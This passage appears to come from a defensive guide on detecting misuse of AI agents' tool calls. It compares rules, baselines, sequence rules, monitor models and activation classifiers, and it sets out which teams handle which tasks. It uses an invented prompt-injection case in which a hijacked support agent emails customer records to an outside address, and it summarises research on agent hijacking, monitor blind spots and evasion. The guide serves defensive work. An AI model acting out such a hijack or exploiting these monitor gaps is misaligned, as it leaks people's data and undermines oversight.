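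Configuration files are the easiest place to start. Claude Code, Cursor and similar programs list their tool servers in files in the user's profile, and these files remain when the agent isn't running. A home-made script may have no such file.

Canale and Soulis tested Agent Detector, their open-source program for finding agents on Windows computers. Every hour it checks which programs are connected to AI services, whether those programs also start a command shell, what is installed or configured, and Windows' records of what has run. It compares what it finds with a catalogue of 39 tools and 184 service addresses. It shows the user a notice they must acknowledge, but doesn't read content or block anything.

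Agents are hard to identify by behaviour alone because ordinary software can behave just like them. A software installer, for example, also connects to a remote service and runs commands. Canale and Soulis call a program that behaves like an agent but talks to a non-AI service a "behavioural twin". They ran 12 synthetic agents, 3 AI components and 9 harmless workloads on one workstation, repeating the test five times. Two simple rules based on behaviour alone flagged all the twins. Agent Detector didn't flag any of them, and it found each agent in the majority of runs.

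That is a good result on false alarms, but "the majority of runs" could mean three out of five. The program detected an intermittently running agent in only about one scan in three. If the scans were independent, eight hourly scans would miss such an agent about 4% of the time, but an agent that always ran briefly between scans might never be detected. The program also missed very short-lived agents, agents inside Windows' built-in Linux system, and connections through undeclared relays, and it doesn't read configuration files stored inside individual projects. Canale and Soulis say their test is too small to rank detectors, but it does support the narrower point that a company should look for the AI service behind a connection, because checking behaviour alone will flag too much ordinary software.

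### Signs of a recording gap

Missing records don't raise alerts, so someone has to look for them. Any of these signs would justify a check:

| Sign | Possible gap | Harmless explanation |
|---|---|---|
| Activity in a database or mail server under an agent's account, with no matching tool call | Calls that bypass the gateway, or an attacker with the agent's token | A scheduled job that shares the account |
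| A bill from an AI provider for more use than the recorded sessions explain | Agents that nobody registered | Developers' test runs |
| A missing sequence number | A lost or deleted record | A record that arrives late |
| Tool server records with no matching trace on the agent's side | A trace ID that got lost on the way | A developer testing the server directly |
| An agent's calls drop to zero while tickets are still being closed | Logging that broke in an update | Staff answering the tickets themselves |
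| Arguments that are suddenly empty | An update that switched content recording off | A tool that takes no arguments |
| No failed tool calls for weeks | Software that ignores the error flag | A quiet period for a reliable tool |

The first check is the most valuable because it doesn't depend on the agent's own logging. Suppose that in one day the invented company's mail server handles 1,000 messages from the support agent's account, but the gateway logs only 940 successful calls to the email tool. Someone has to explain the 60 messages without a logged call. They should also compare recipients, since a poisoned email tool that adds a blind copy to every message would leave the two totals equal.

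## Detecting misuse in the records

Five methods can detect misuse in the records: fixed rules, comparison with a baseline of normal activity, rules over a sequence of calls, monitor models, and classifiers that read the agent model's internal activations. They are listed roughly from least to most expensive. The order is only rough because an activation classifier is cheap to run but expensive to build.

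The attack on the invented company's support agent is a useful test for all of them. The agent read the ticket, looked up seven different customers, and then sent the malicious email as the ninth call of its session.

### Fixed rules

A fixed rule is a condition that a program checks against each record. The simplest one for the support agent would raise an alert whenever the agent emails an address that isn't on the ticket. The gateway already records whether the address is on the ticket, so the rule would catch the malicious email. It would also raise an alert whenever a customer asks the agent to send a copy to their accountant.

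Rules like this take almost no time to run. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, 2026) reports a median of 5.7 microseconds to check one call against a written plan. At that speed, checking all 200,000 of the invented company's daily calls would take just over a second.

Rules that separate misuse from ordinary work are hard to write. Splunk, which sells software for searching logs, publishes ready-made rules for MCP servers in its *Analytics Story*, including rules for suspicious database queries and file writes. But Soto concedes in *When AI Tools Turn Against You* that a malicious instruction can be exactly the same as a harmless one. Mooney suggests searching tool arguments for characters such as semicolons, which attackers use to add their own command to a query. This works for a search field with a fixed format, but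 it would also flag ordinary punctuation in the body of an email.

Fixed rules work best when the condition is itself a breach of policy. Canale and Soulis point out that whether a tool is authorised depends on identity and policy, and not on how the tool behaves. A rule for unapproved tool servers therefore needs only a good inventory:

```
Rule:      tool server not on the approved list
Check:     every tool call, every tools/list reply, and the
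           configuration files on staff machines
Condition: the server's address or program hash is not in
           the inventory
Threshold: 1 occurrence
Grouping:  one alert per server and machine per day
Exception: machines registered for testing
```

The rule ignores the server's self-reported name. Besides experiments by staff, an out-of-date inventory will set it off.

A second policy rule catches changed tools:

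```
Rule:      tool description differs from the approved version
Check:     every tools/list reply
Condition: the hash of the description and schema differs from
           the approved hash for that server and tool
Threshold: 1 difference
Grouping:  one alert per tool and new hash
```

The grouping matters because thousands of sessions could load the same changed tool in a day. The software should also put the fields in a fixed order before computing the hash, or a harmless reordering will look like a change. Mooney's examples of suspicious changes include new instructions inside a tag marked "important". A change like that would justify putting the alert at the top of the queue.

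This rule doesn't assess whether the new description is malicious, which is much harder to determine. *MalTool* (2026) tested scanners that do, and those from Tencent and AntGroup typically flagged between 30% and more than 50% of harmless tools. The rule still can't detect hidden code.

A company can also write a fixed rule for each task. In Shavit's system, a language model is given the user's request and the available tools, and it lists the tools the task needs before the agent reads any outside text. Shavit, who works at the security company Silverfort, tested this on logs from AgentDojo, a public test set in which agents do office, banking, travel and chat tasks while exposed to hidden instructions meant to hijack them. Blocking every tool not on the list would have cut successful attacks from 45.7% to 10.2%, but it would also have blocked a step in 16.2% of harmless tasks. Adding limits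 on arguments, such as who may receive a message, would have cut successful attacks to 5.5% but blocked a step in 32.9% of harmless tasks. Only the argument limits would help with the support agent, because an ordinary billing complaint may require all three of the agent's tools.

The logs came from GPT-4o, a 2024 model that was fairly easy to hijack. None of the 20 attacks Shavit tried on the newer GPT-5.2 succeeded. The figures for harmless tasks may be the more useful ones today, since they depend less on how easily an attacker can fool the agent.

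### Comparison with a normal baseline

A baseline rule compares an agent with its own past. Its main use is to catch runaway repetition and sudden bulk activity:

```
Rule:      calls far above the agent's baseline
Check:     after every call
Condition: (a) the session has more than 60 calls, and more than
               99.9% of that agent's sessions in the past 28 days
           or
           (b) the agent has called one tool 15 times in the
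               session with identical arguments
Threshold: 1 session
```

The minimum of 60 calls is three times the invented company's usual 20. Without it, the rule would flag about one session in 1,000, or ten a day, even if nothing was wrong. A new agent has no history, so at first the company can apply only the fixed numbers.

The rule would miss the attack on the support agent because that session had only nine calls. A baseline for the number of customers looked up per ticket would catch it, since the usual number is one. Choosing what to count therefore matters more than choosing a more sophisticated statistical method. Mooney also recommends tracking failed calls and treating a spike in calls followed by unusual queries as a stronger signal than either alone.

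In Shavit's tests, detectors looked for unusual behaviour in the mix of tools, the variety of arguments and the timing of calls. With thresholds that flagged 5% of harmless calls, they caught only 7% to 12% of hijacked calls, while checking calls against the task's plan caught 76%. When a different person took over a session, the plan was useless because the new person's requests defined a new task, but the better behavioural detector caught 24% of the calls. The sessions were artificial and came from 12 simulated users, so the exact rates mean little. Still, the results suggest using behavioural baselines to detect stolen accounts and the task to detect hijacked agents.

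Counting calls is cheap. The larger cost is keeping the baseline current through product recalls, month ends and new agent versions.

### Rules over a sequence of calls

Some misuse is visible only in the order of events. *ToolGuardian* (2026) gives an example in which an agent reads a database and then updates a project on GitHub, a site for sharing code. The task permits both actions, but the system blocks the update because sensitive data could leave with it. At the invented company, the same idea gives a rule for the harm at the top of its list:

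```
Rule:      bulk read, then a message to a new outside address
Step 1:    the agent reads the records of 5 or more customers
Step 2:    the agent sends a message outside the company
Condition: the address was not in the customer database when
           the session began
Window:    one session; also, all sessions that write to the
           same address within 24 hours
Threshold: 1 occurrence
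```

The support agent read seven customers' records and then wrote to `archive@outside.example`, which triggers the rule. The 24-hour window catches an attacker who takes four records at a time through several tickets. An address that appears only in the ticket doesn't count as known, because anyone can write a ticket.

The rule would also raise an alert if a business customer with five staff accounts asked for a summary to be sent to its new bookkeeper. It would miss the theft of a single record, or a theft by an existing customer. Five is a starting point, and the company should run the rule over a month of old records to see how many alerts it would have produced.

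*Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) measured how much this kind of history helps. The researchers started with five general rules, each requiring approval before a risky type of action, such as a payment, a deletion or an outgoing message. On recorded AgentDojo runs, the rules flagged 70.1% of 1,931 successful attacks and 29.3% of 123 harmless runs. The recordings contained no approvals, so the rules flagged every risky action. In the banking tasks, they flagged 97.4% of the attacks but also 79.2% of the harmless runs.

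They then wrote a rule that flagged a payment only if the payee hadn't appeared in account data earlier in the session. Flagging every payment had caught 79.2% of attacks and flagged 44% of harmless runs, while the new rule caught 70.0% of attacks and flagged 24% of harmless runs. A similar rule for emails to unknown recipients reduced the share of harmless runs flagged from 15.2% to 10.9%, and the share of attacks caught from 42.5% to 39.2%. The rates are uncertain because there were only 25 harmless banking runs and 46 harmless office runs, though results pooled across other models moved in the same direction.

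Even at 10.9%, the invented company would have 1,090 flagged sessions a day, so its rule also requires a bulk read. The rule still needs little computing power, but the software has to store each session's earlier events, and a missing or late record can break the sequence.

Rules about tool calls also can't detect harm that depends on what a text means. Kekatos and colleagues applied their general rules to R-Judge, a collection of labelled agent records, and the rules flagged only 23.6% of the unsafe records, along with 16.3% of the safe ones. Most of the harm was in the content, such as leaked private details or dangerous advice.

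### Monitor models

A monitor model can read the content. Given the support agent's session, it could recognise that one billing complaint doesn't require seven customers' records, even if nobody had written a rule with a threshold of five.

*Towards a Unified Misuse Monitoring Benchmark* (Pramod, Oldfield and Bibi, October 2026) is the broadest comparison of such monitors. Its roughly 6,200 sessions cover prompt injection through tool results and decomposition attacks, in which the user splits a harmful goal into small requests that each look innocent on their own.

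For the decomposition attacks, the researchers took 582 harmful and 583 harmless series of requests from an earlier dataset. Google's Gemma 4 model wrote the agent's replies and tool calls and simulated the tools' results. They also made 582 sessions by mixing harmless requests into the harmful series, and 1,644 in which the agent refuses partway through. For the injection attacks, they cut real AgentDojo logs just after the hostile text and had Gemma continue them, which produced 2,828 sessions. In some the agent obeys the attacker, and in others it ignores the instruction and finishes the user's task.

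The researchers compared 17 monitoring set-ups. Fourteen prompted a general model in different ways, and three used ready-made safety classifiers. The set-ups differed in how much of the session the monitor saw, how often it gave a score, and whether it judged the conversation or the agent's actions. In each harmful session, they also marked a window from the agent's first harmful step to the call that completes the attacker's goal, and checked whether the monitor's first flag fell inside it.

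These are results for four of the set-ups, with Gemma 4 as the monitor and at most 10% of harmless sessions flagged:

| What the monitor reads and judges | Decomposition: caught | Decomposition: first flag in window | Injection: caught | Injection: first flag in window |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Current message only; judges the action | 78% | 33% | 82% | 62% |
| Session so far; judges the requests together | 96% | 17% | No usable threshold | – |
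| Session so far; judges the latest action | 94% | 43% | 99.7% | 95% |
| Suspicious passages it has extracted; judges those | 93% | 50% | 99.5% | 90% |

The monitor that judged the requests together failed on injection. It flagged at least 63% of harmless sessions at every threshold. Its AUC, the chance that it scores a random harmful session above a random harmless one, was 0.52, about the same as a coin toss. Having the same model judge the latest action raised the AUC to 0.99, probably because the harmless sessions contain the same hostile text as the harmful ones and only the agent's response differs. A company should therefore have its monitor check whether the latest call fits the task, not whether the session contains anything suspicious. Otherwise, every hostile ticket that the agent correctly ignores could raise an alert.

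Most flags outside the window came too early, often when the agent was only preparing. An early flag does little damage if an analyst reads the session later, but it matters if the flag stops the agent. The monitors also handled refusals badly. With most models, the set-ups that judged actions still flagged 28% to 48% of sessions in which the agent refused at the point where it would first have done harm.

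Results will probably be worse on real traffic. One model wrote all the continuations and tool results, so the sessions may be more alike than real ones. AI models marked where harm began in the decomposition attacks, and two of these models chose exactly the same message in only 67.5% of the 40 sessions checked. Pramod and colleagues also chose some thresholds on the same data they used for scoring. When they fixed the thresholds beforehand, the share of decomposition attacks flagged inside the window fell by about 12 percentage points on average. An attacker who knows how a monitor works may be able to evade it. Flagging 10% of harmless sessions would give the invented company 1,000 alerts a day, nearly all of them false because misuse is rare.

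False alarms can be hard to predict. Mola, Guo and Potts report in *Evaluating our AI Guard application to improve quality and control cost* that Datadog's monitor flagged a request for maths help because the answer included Python code.

Monitor models cost far more to run than rules. At the invented company, a session's records come to about 80 KB, or 20,000 tokens (short pieces of text that models process) at four characters each. At an assumed price of $1 per million tokens, reading every session once would cost $200 a day. If the monitor instead reread the whole session so far after every call, it would process about 210,000 tokens per session and cost $2,100 a day. Reusing earlier computation would reduce the difference.

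Showing the monitor less text saves money and can improve its judgement. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a monitor that sees only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations, which might persuade the monitor to accept a bad action, and the tool results, which might contain an attacker's instructions. Including them made the monitor worse at spotting actions that went beyond the user's request. At the invented company, this design would also hide the ticket, which arrives as a tool result. The monitor would still see a billing task, seven searches, and an email that the gateway has marked as not matching the ticket.

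### Classifiers on the model's activations

While a language model processes text, it represents each token as a long list of numbers called activations. A small classifier can use these numbers to estimate whether something harmful is happening. The model computes the activations anyway, so the classifier adds little work.

*Monitoring Activations for Real-Time Detection of Cyber Misuse* (Alfano, Stein and colleagues, 2026) describes a classifier that the researchers built for their employer Reflection AI's Beam model and tested in November. They trained it on about a million labelled passages from 52,387 conversations, many of them from an automated attacker that tried to get agents to do harmful hacking tasks. Another AI system labelled passages as harmful or harmless and left unclear ones unlabelled.

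Each monitor's threshold was set to flag at most 5% of harmless validation sessions. On new sessions, the classifier caught 93.1% of harmful passages, while Kimi K3, a general language model reading the text, caught 72.7%. The classifier flagged 5.44% of the harmless test sessions and 0.56% of a separate set of 3,217 ordinary coding sessions.

The comparison favours the classifier somewhat. The classifier was trained on the same kind of data and labels used in the test, while Kimi K3 had one prompt and one attempt at each passage. The scoring also left out passages that were too unclear to label. On a separate test of single requests, the text monitors did better when few false alarms were allowed. The study is good evidence for using a specialised classifier on long hacking sessions, but it doesn't show that reading activations is better in general.

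Beam's output fell by only 0.6% with 64 users at once when the classifier ran on its own graphics processor. But this meant adding a processor to the four running the model, so output per processor fell by about 20%. When the classifier shared one of the four, output fell by 4.8%, and the typical wait for the first token rose from 288 to 385 milliseconds.

For the support agent, such a classifier might raise an alert while the model is still writing the email call. But Alfano and colleagues tested only cyber misuse, and the classifier may not distinguish stealing customer records by email from ordinary customer service. The company would need labelled examples of the kinds of misuse it wants to detect. The classifier also needs access to the model's activations, so the company would generally have to run the model itself or rely on the provider to run the classifier.

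### Layers that few products cover

Buying a product won't fill every gap. Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues (2026), in *MCP-DPT*, surveyed 13 defences for MCP in April and rated them against 49 attacks. They sorted the attacks by the part of the system that should stop them first:

| Layer | Highest share of attacks covered by one product | Products covering none |
|---|---|---|
| Language model | 44% | 5 of 13 |
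| Application that runs the agent | 38% | 3 of 13 |
| Client software | 36% | 5 of 13 |
| Tool server | 50% | 3 of 13 |
| Network connection | 50% | 10 of 13 |
| Registries and software supply | 100% | 4 of 13 |

"Covered" means that a product could reasonably detect, block or limit an attack. Rostamzadeh and colleagues did not measure how often the products would succeed, so actual detection rates are probably lower than the coverage percentages. Their text and tables are also inconsistent about some products, so those percentages are approximate.

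The network connection is the clearest gap. A company can partly fill it by comparing the arguments the agent's software sent with those the tool server received, since any difference would mean something changed the message on the way. For the application that runs the agent, the survey found no product covering attacks that change the order of the agent's calls or overload the agent with expensive ones. The sequence and baseline rules above address those two problems.

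### Before the call, during the session or afterwards

The same method can be much more or less useful depending on when it runs.

| When the check runs | Delay | Cost of a false alarm | Harm already done |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before the call | Microseconds for a rule; often seconds for a model | A harmless action stops | None from this call, but earlier calls have run |
| During the session | Often one or more calls behind | A harmless session may stop halfway | Whatever ran before the agent stopped |
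| Afterwards | Minutes to hours | An analyst's time | Possibly all of it |

Only a check before the call can keep the customer records from leaving, but it makes the agent wait. Microsoft's agent-building product, Copilot Studio, lets an outside security service allow or block each proposed tool call. Microsoft gives the service one second to respond, and originally let the agent continue if no answer came. According to CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, the customer can now choose whether a timeout allows or blocks the call. That choice matters for slower monitors, such as the reasoning model Shavit used to review flagged calls. It took a median of 3.6 seconds, so most of its answers would miss the one-second limit.

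Anthropic reduces the delay by running its monitor in two stages. A quick check gives a yes-or-no answer, and a slower one reasons only about the calls the quick check flags. On 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic's staff, the quick check alone would have blocked 8.5% of harmless calls, and the two together would have blocked 0.4%. But the second stage also let more bad actions through. The full system missed 17% of 52 real cases in which the agent went beyond what its user wanted. With so few cases, the true rate could be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. Real examples are scarce elsewhere too, so OpenAI tests its own pre-call reviewer on partly synthetic cases.

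If the rate of 0.4% per call held at the invented company and errors were independent, about 7.7% of its 20-call sessions would contain at least one false block. That is tolerable only if a block doesn't end the session. Anthropic's monitor gives the agent the reason for the block, and the agent tries another approach. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, a person has to step in. Copilot Studio instead stops the agent and notifies the user that it has blocked their message.

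A monitor model can handle routine approvals much better than a person. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment in which 1,053 paid testers working with a coding agent were asked to approve a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of them refused, while the monitor blocked 89% of the same commands. In real use at Anthropic, the monitor stopped an agent from publishing an internal report on a public website after an upload to a company drive failed.

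Less obvious misuse is harder to detect. BestHub's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* summarises an outside test in which the system let through 81% of 142 actions that exceeded the user's permission and blocked 19.8% of acceptable ones. The account is second-hand and the test was designed to be difficult, but the results are a good reason not to assume that the 89% applies to every kind of misuse.

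Checks during a session avoid the wait, but they can prevent harm only if a warning comes first. In the AgentDojo attacks that Kekatos and colleagues studied, their general rules went off before the final harmful call in 52.4% of cases, only at that call in 17.7%, and never in 29.9%. Early warnings typically came one call ahead. The support agent's session would give slightly more time, since the agent reads a fifth customer's record at the sixth call and sends the email at the ninth. Three calls may take only a few seconds, so software would have to pause the agent automatically.

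A monitor that checks afterwards can read the whole session and compare it with the mail server's log, and its mistakes interrupt nobody, but it detects misuse late. One Splunk rule for suspicious database queries runs every hour and covers the period from 70 to 10 minutes before each run. A check on the same schedule would find the malicious email 10 to 70 minutes after the agent sent it.

The invented company could reasonably hold a call before it runs if the call uses a changed tool, deletes logs or sends a message to a new outside address after a bulk read. It could apply the baseline rule during the session and pause agents that exceed it. A monitor model could read each session after it ends, for about $200 a day at the assumed price.

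## Dividing the work between application security, engineering and security operations

The fictional company's detection plan creates work for several teams, which must approve the tool servers, keep the records complete, read the alerts and, if necessary, stop an agent outside working hours. Most of this work is ongoing because the tools and agents keep changing.

### Nine tasks

| Task | What it produces | What the person has to know |
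|---|---|---|
| 1. Approve a tool server | An inventory entry with an owner, the agents that may use the server, and a hash of each tool's definition | What the server can reach and who wrote it |
| 2. Say what must be detected | A list of misuse, with the evidence for each item | Which harms would hurt the company most |
| 3. Produce the logs | Records with the user, task, session, arguments and decision | How the agent and its tools work |
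| 4. Keep the logs flowing | Regular checks for gaps, and repairs | How many records a normal day produces |
| 5. Write and tune rules | Rules that someone has tried on old records | The log format and the usual harmless explanations |
| 6. Review alerts | A decision on each alert, with the reason | What the agent was supposed to be doing |
| 7. Stop an agent | A halted session, tool or agent | Which control to use and what else depends on it |
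| 8. Revoke credentials | Tokens that no system accepts any more | Where the agent's tokens are valid |
| 9. Fix the cause | A changed tool, permission or agent | Why the misuse was possible |

Companies can easily merge tasks 3 and 4 by mistake. Producing the logs is a project that an engineer can finish in a few weeks, but keeping them flowing has no end date, so that task may have no owner once the project closes. Tasks 7 and 8 are separate because a token can remain valid after the work it was issued for has ended.

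No team has all the knowledge in the last column. Application security knows the servers it has reviewed, engineering knows how the agents behave, and security operations knows how to investigate and may be the only one of the three working at night.

### Three arrangements and how they fail

A company could make application security responsible for detection on tool servers. Its reviewers have just studied each server when they approve it, so they know which calls would be dangerous and can write a detection rule the same week. But they usually work office hours and move on to the next server when they finish. They also know more about individual servers than about what an agent does with several of them in one session. For example, the support agent's customer search and email tool might come from two servers that each look acceptable alone, but together they could let the agent email customer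 data to an outsider.

This arrangement is likely to fail when a tool changes. Suppose the mail server's developers rename `send_email` to `send_message`. A reviewer sees the changed definition, finds nothing wrong and approves it. Nobody remembers that the rule for detecting bulk reads followed by a message looks for the old name, so the rule stops matching anything. It produces no error, and the lack of alerts looks like a month without attacks. Comparing the number of messages the support agent sends with the number the rule examines would expose the problem, because the agent still sends 1,000 a day and the rule has examined none since the update.

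Each engineering team could instead monitor the agents it runs. These engineers can recognise odd behaviour quickly, and the person who reads the alert can often repair the fault. This works best for faults such as runaway repetition, which an engineer on call would want to know about anyway. The main objection is that a team under pressure to keep its agent running also decides whether the agent has done something wrong. Teams will also write different rules and keep different records.

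Attacks that involve more than one team's agents can then go undetected. If an attacker takes four customers' records through the support agent and four more through a billing agent, neither team sees enough to meet its alert threshold of five. To catch the attack, someone would have to notice the same outside address in both logs. Other signs of failure are easier to find, such as a team that has had no alerts for six months while similar teams have them weekly, or a list of exceptions that only grows.

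The third option is a central security operations team that uses one shared platform. The team can search across all agents, and in many companies it already works through the night. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend managing agent security within a company's existing security frameworks rather than as a separate discipline, which favours this arrangement. But an analyst may lack the context to know whether looking up seven customers is normal for a billing complaint, and the platform can't show calls that never reach it.

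When a central team lacks context, its analysts start to close alerts as "expected behaviour" without explaining why. Others send the alert to engineering and wait. A manager can look for closures without a reason, questions that engineering hasn't answered for days, and agents in the inventory that have never sent a record. The renamed email tool would also cause trouble with a central team, perhaps for longer, because the people who maintain the rule didn't help approve the change.

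In a company that already has a night shift, the central team is best placed to handle rules and alerts. Its analysts can't change the software, so producing logs and fixing agents is better left to the teams that can.

### How Microsoft, Maryland and the NCSC assign the work

Microsoft's advice to its customers starts with the approval of tool servers. Its *Define MCP Server and Tool Approval Policy* describes three ways these servers enter a company that uses Agent 365, Microsoft's platform for managing agents: Microsoft adds them to its catalogue, outside vendors publish them, and the company's own developers build them. By default, none of these routes includes a security review.

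Microsoft advises customers to decide who reviews new servers, and suggests the security team, the platform engineers or a joint board. The reviewers should check what data the server can access, how it authenticates callers and what audit trail it can provide. A server from an outside vendor also needs a vendor risk assessment, while one built in-house needs a code and architecture review. Microsoft can reasonably leave the choice of reviewer open in general advice, but a company that copies the wording without choosing has a policy that nobody is assigned to carry out.

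Inside Microsoft, the IT organisation and the chief information security officer's team run MCP security together. Microsoft requires the owner of a server to declare its tools, the data it accesses, how callers authenticate, where it runs and who is on call. Analysts therefore know whom to call when the first alert arrives. Reviewers then test the server as a client would, including by attempting prompt injection. Microsoft publishes the server only after security, privacy and responsible-AI reviews, and once written response procedures are in place. Owners and security staff also see the same dashboards, which should reduce arguments about what happened.

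Microsoft is still "working toward" logging tool calls and authorisation decisions from end to end, and toward finding unknown servers automatically. It writes of "no blind spots", but recommending that remote servers sit behind its gateway can't guarantee that on its own. It reports faster reviews and fewer unapproved servers but gives no figures. Its practice is a useful model for dividing the work, but weak evidence of how well that division works.

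Maryland gives approval to one office. Bhatt (2026), in *MCP Server Security*, sets out the state's rules for its employees and contractors in version 2.0, revised on 8 September. The Office of Security Management approves every server, keeps the registry and assigns each server to one of three authentication tiers:

| Tier | Servers | Authentication |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Local servers that make no calls to remote services | None |
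| 2 | Remote servers on which every tool is read-only | The OAuth 2.0 standard preferred; a managed key allowed if the vendor doesn't support it |
| 3 | Servers that can change or send anything, or that handle the state's more sensitive data | OAuth 2.0, without exception |

Staff can't choose their own tier. If the office can't verify that a server is read-only, the server goes into tier 3, so the requesting agency or vendor has to produce the evidence. The invented company's mail server would be in tier 3 because it sends messages.

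Maryland separates the first response to suspected misuse from the investigation. Staff disconnect their AI client from the server, preserve the logs and contact the state's security operations centre within an hour. Bhatt tells them not to investigate or repair anything themselves. The centre analyses the evidence, notifies the people affected and decides what to report to regulators. These instructions suit staff who aren't trained to investigate, because they might otherwise delete evidence while trying to fix the problem.

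The guidance covers detection in much less detail. Remote servers must send their logs to central, tamper-resistant storage, but Bhatt doesn't name anyone to write detection rules or watch those logs. Other state policies may assign that work. As written, the process starts when a person notices something odd. The security office reassesses a server's tier when someone notifies it of a new capability, whereas Microsoft automatically compares tool descriptions and sends changes back for review. The automatic check is safer because a vendor may not announce a change.

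The UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), one of the agencies behind the joint guidance, issued interim advice in August 2026. Turner's *NCSC Publishes Interim Guidance on Agentic AI Security* reports that, for higher-risk uses, the NCSC recommends making named individuals or groups responsible for an agent's activity and monitoring it in real time. The NCSC also advises companies to include agents in security operations and incident response in much the same way as human users. Formal guidance will replace the interim advice, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems*.

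In an earlier article, reprinted by New Business, the NCSC says a company should decide who owns an agent, who approves its access, who monitors it, who reviews incidents and who can stop it before connecting it to real systems. The NCSC adds that these people need the power and the incentive to intervene. Assigning someone a role doesn't help much if they expect to get in trouble for interrupting the business.

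The NCSC doesn't say which team should hold each role. Singapore's framework, as summarised in Mondaq's *Singapore's Agentic AI Framework*, divides responsibilities between decision makers, product teams and cybersecurity teams. That is close to the division here, but the framework doesn't assign individual tasks.

### A responsibility table for the invented company

The following table shows one defensible way to split the work. People who are consulted give advice before a decision, and people who are informed hear about it afterwards. Each agent's owner is the engineering manager in charge of it.

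| Task | Responsible | Accountable | Consulted | Informed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Approve a tool server, or a change to one | Application security reviewer | Head of application security | Engineers who want the server; security operations | Owners of agents that will use it |
| 2. Say what must be detected | Application security | Head of application security | Agent owners; security operations | Engineering teams |
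| 3. Produce the logs | Engineers who build the agent | Agent's owner | Application security; security operations | Gateway team |
| 4. Keep the logs flowing | Gateway team, in engineering | Gateway team's manager | Security operations; agent's engineers | Application security |
| 5. Write and tune rules | Rule writers in security operations | Head of security operations | Application security; agent's engineers | Agent's owner |
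| 6. Review alerts | Analyst on shift | Head of security operations | Agent's on-call engineer | Agent's owner, if the misuse is real |
| 7. Stop an agent | Analyst on shift | Head of security operations | On-call engineer, if there is time | Agent's owner; the department that uses the agent |
| 8. Revoke credentials | Analyst on shift, using a prepared procedure | Head of security operations | On-call engineer | Agent's owner; application security |
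| 9. Fix the cause | Agent's engineers | Agent's owner | Application security; security operations | Owners of agents with the same tools |

Application security decides what to detect, and security operations writes the rules. If one team did both, it might list only the harms it already knew how to detect. Separating the tasks also gives application security a reason to check, a month later, whether every harm on its list has a rule.

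The gateway team's manager answers for the flow of logs because analysts who notice a gap can't repair the software. Engineering also fixes the cause of an incident, but security operations decides when to close the alert so that the team that made the mistake doesn't judge its own repair.

Security operations is consulted on every approval, including approvals of changes, to deal with cases like the renamed email tool. The reviewer shouldn't complete the approval until a rule writer has confirmed that the rules still match the new definition. This will delay some harmless updates by a day or so.

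The main argument against this split is that it creates hand-offs between teams. A new rule can involve all three, and a company with good engineers on call might reasonably send alerts about runaway repetition straight to them. The table also assigns only individual tasks, so someone still has to answer for whether the monitoring as a whole catches misuse.

A firm of 30 people with one security specialist can't fill all these roles. The specialist could do tasks 1, 2 and 5, the engineers tasks 3, 4 and 9, and an outside monitoring service could review alerts at night. The service would need written authority to stop an agent and revoke its credentials, because the firm's own staff would be asleep. Without such a service, the firm could limit its agents to office hours. Turner reports that the NCSC suggests starting this way even if an organisation plans to run agents overnight later.

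Even at a small firm, nobody should be the only reviewer of a tool server they wrote, or the only person to close alerts about an agent they run. A second person's check might take ten minutes a week.

### When a provider runs part of the system

Many companies don't operate the whole agent themselves. OpenAI distinguishes enterprise-managed agents from platform-managed agents. With an enterprise-managed agent, the company controls the software loop, the machines it runs on, the credentials and the access controls, while a provider runs the model and processes the data sent to it. With a platform-managed agent, the provider also operates the platform and the loop, and often takes on responsibility for securing that service and keeping customers' data separate.

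The company still decides who may use a platform-managed agent, which data it can reach, what authority it has and when a person must approve an action. If the platform stores credentials, the provider has to protect them, but the company has to limit what they give access to. OpenAI also says that whoever deployed the agent remains responsible for the outcome. OpenAI benefits from that view as a provider, but customers whose records leak will probably also hold the deploying company responsible.

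OpenAI doesn't divide the work task by task. Applied to the tasks that change most, its distinction would give:

| Task | Enterprise-managed agent | Platform-managed agent |
|---|---|---|
| Produce the logs | The company, except for records inside the model service | The provider for the agent's session; the company for its own mail server and databases |
| Keep the logs flowing | The company | The provider up to the point of delivery; the company after that |
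| Stop an agent | The company | The company, through controls that the provider supplies |
| Revoke credentials | The company | The provider for tokens it holds; the company for the accounts behind them |
| Fix the cause | The company, unless the fault is in the model service | The provider for the platform; the company for permissions and instructions |

Some agents combine the two, such as a provider's remote agent that calls a tool server inside the company's network. OpenAI notes that the company is still responsible for managing the server, even though the request came from outside. Here, the invented company would have the log of the email but might have to ask the provider for the ticket text that led to it.

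The contract should therefore specify which records the provider will deliver, how quickly, and how long it will keep them. It should also specify whether the company can stop a session without calling anyone, whether stopping it invalidates the tokens, and whom to phone at night. The company still decides what to detect, writes the rules and reviews the alerts, unless it pays someone else to do so.

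### Who may stop an agent

Speed matters more for stopping an agent than for any other task, so the analyst needs permission in advance. Microsoft recommends graded responses, such as blocking destructive actions while still allowing reads, and has controls for stopping agents at both the client and the gateway. At the invented company, the limits could be:

| Action | Who may order it | What it interrupts |
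|---|---|---|
| Hold one call | The gateway, under a rule approved beforehand | One step of one task |
| End one session | Analyst on shift | One ticket |
| Block one tool for one agent | Analyst on shift | For the email tool, about 1,000 messages a day |
| Stop one agent | Analyst on shift, who then tells its owner | All of that agent's work |
| Stop every agent | Head of security operations or a named deputy | All 10,000 sessions a day |

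The automatic hold fits OpenAI's advice to limit automated responses to well-defined containment steps and leave serious or unclear cases to people. The last row needs a deputy because the head of security operations will sometimes be unreachable.

Blocking the support agent's email by mistake delays some replies, but waiting for permission to block it may let more records leave, and nobody can recall them. The company should therefore prefer a mistaken block to a late one, and shouldn't hold a reasonable but wrong decision against the analyst. Microsoft also rehearses its stop controls so that nobody uses one for the first time during an incident.

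Ending the agent's process may not be enough. Turner reports that the NCSC also wants companies to be able to quickly cut an agent's network access and its connection to the model. At the invented company, the gateway could block the agent's calls even if its process kept running, but not stop a tool running on the agent's own machine.

### One alert from 02:10 to closure

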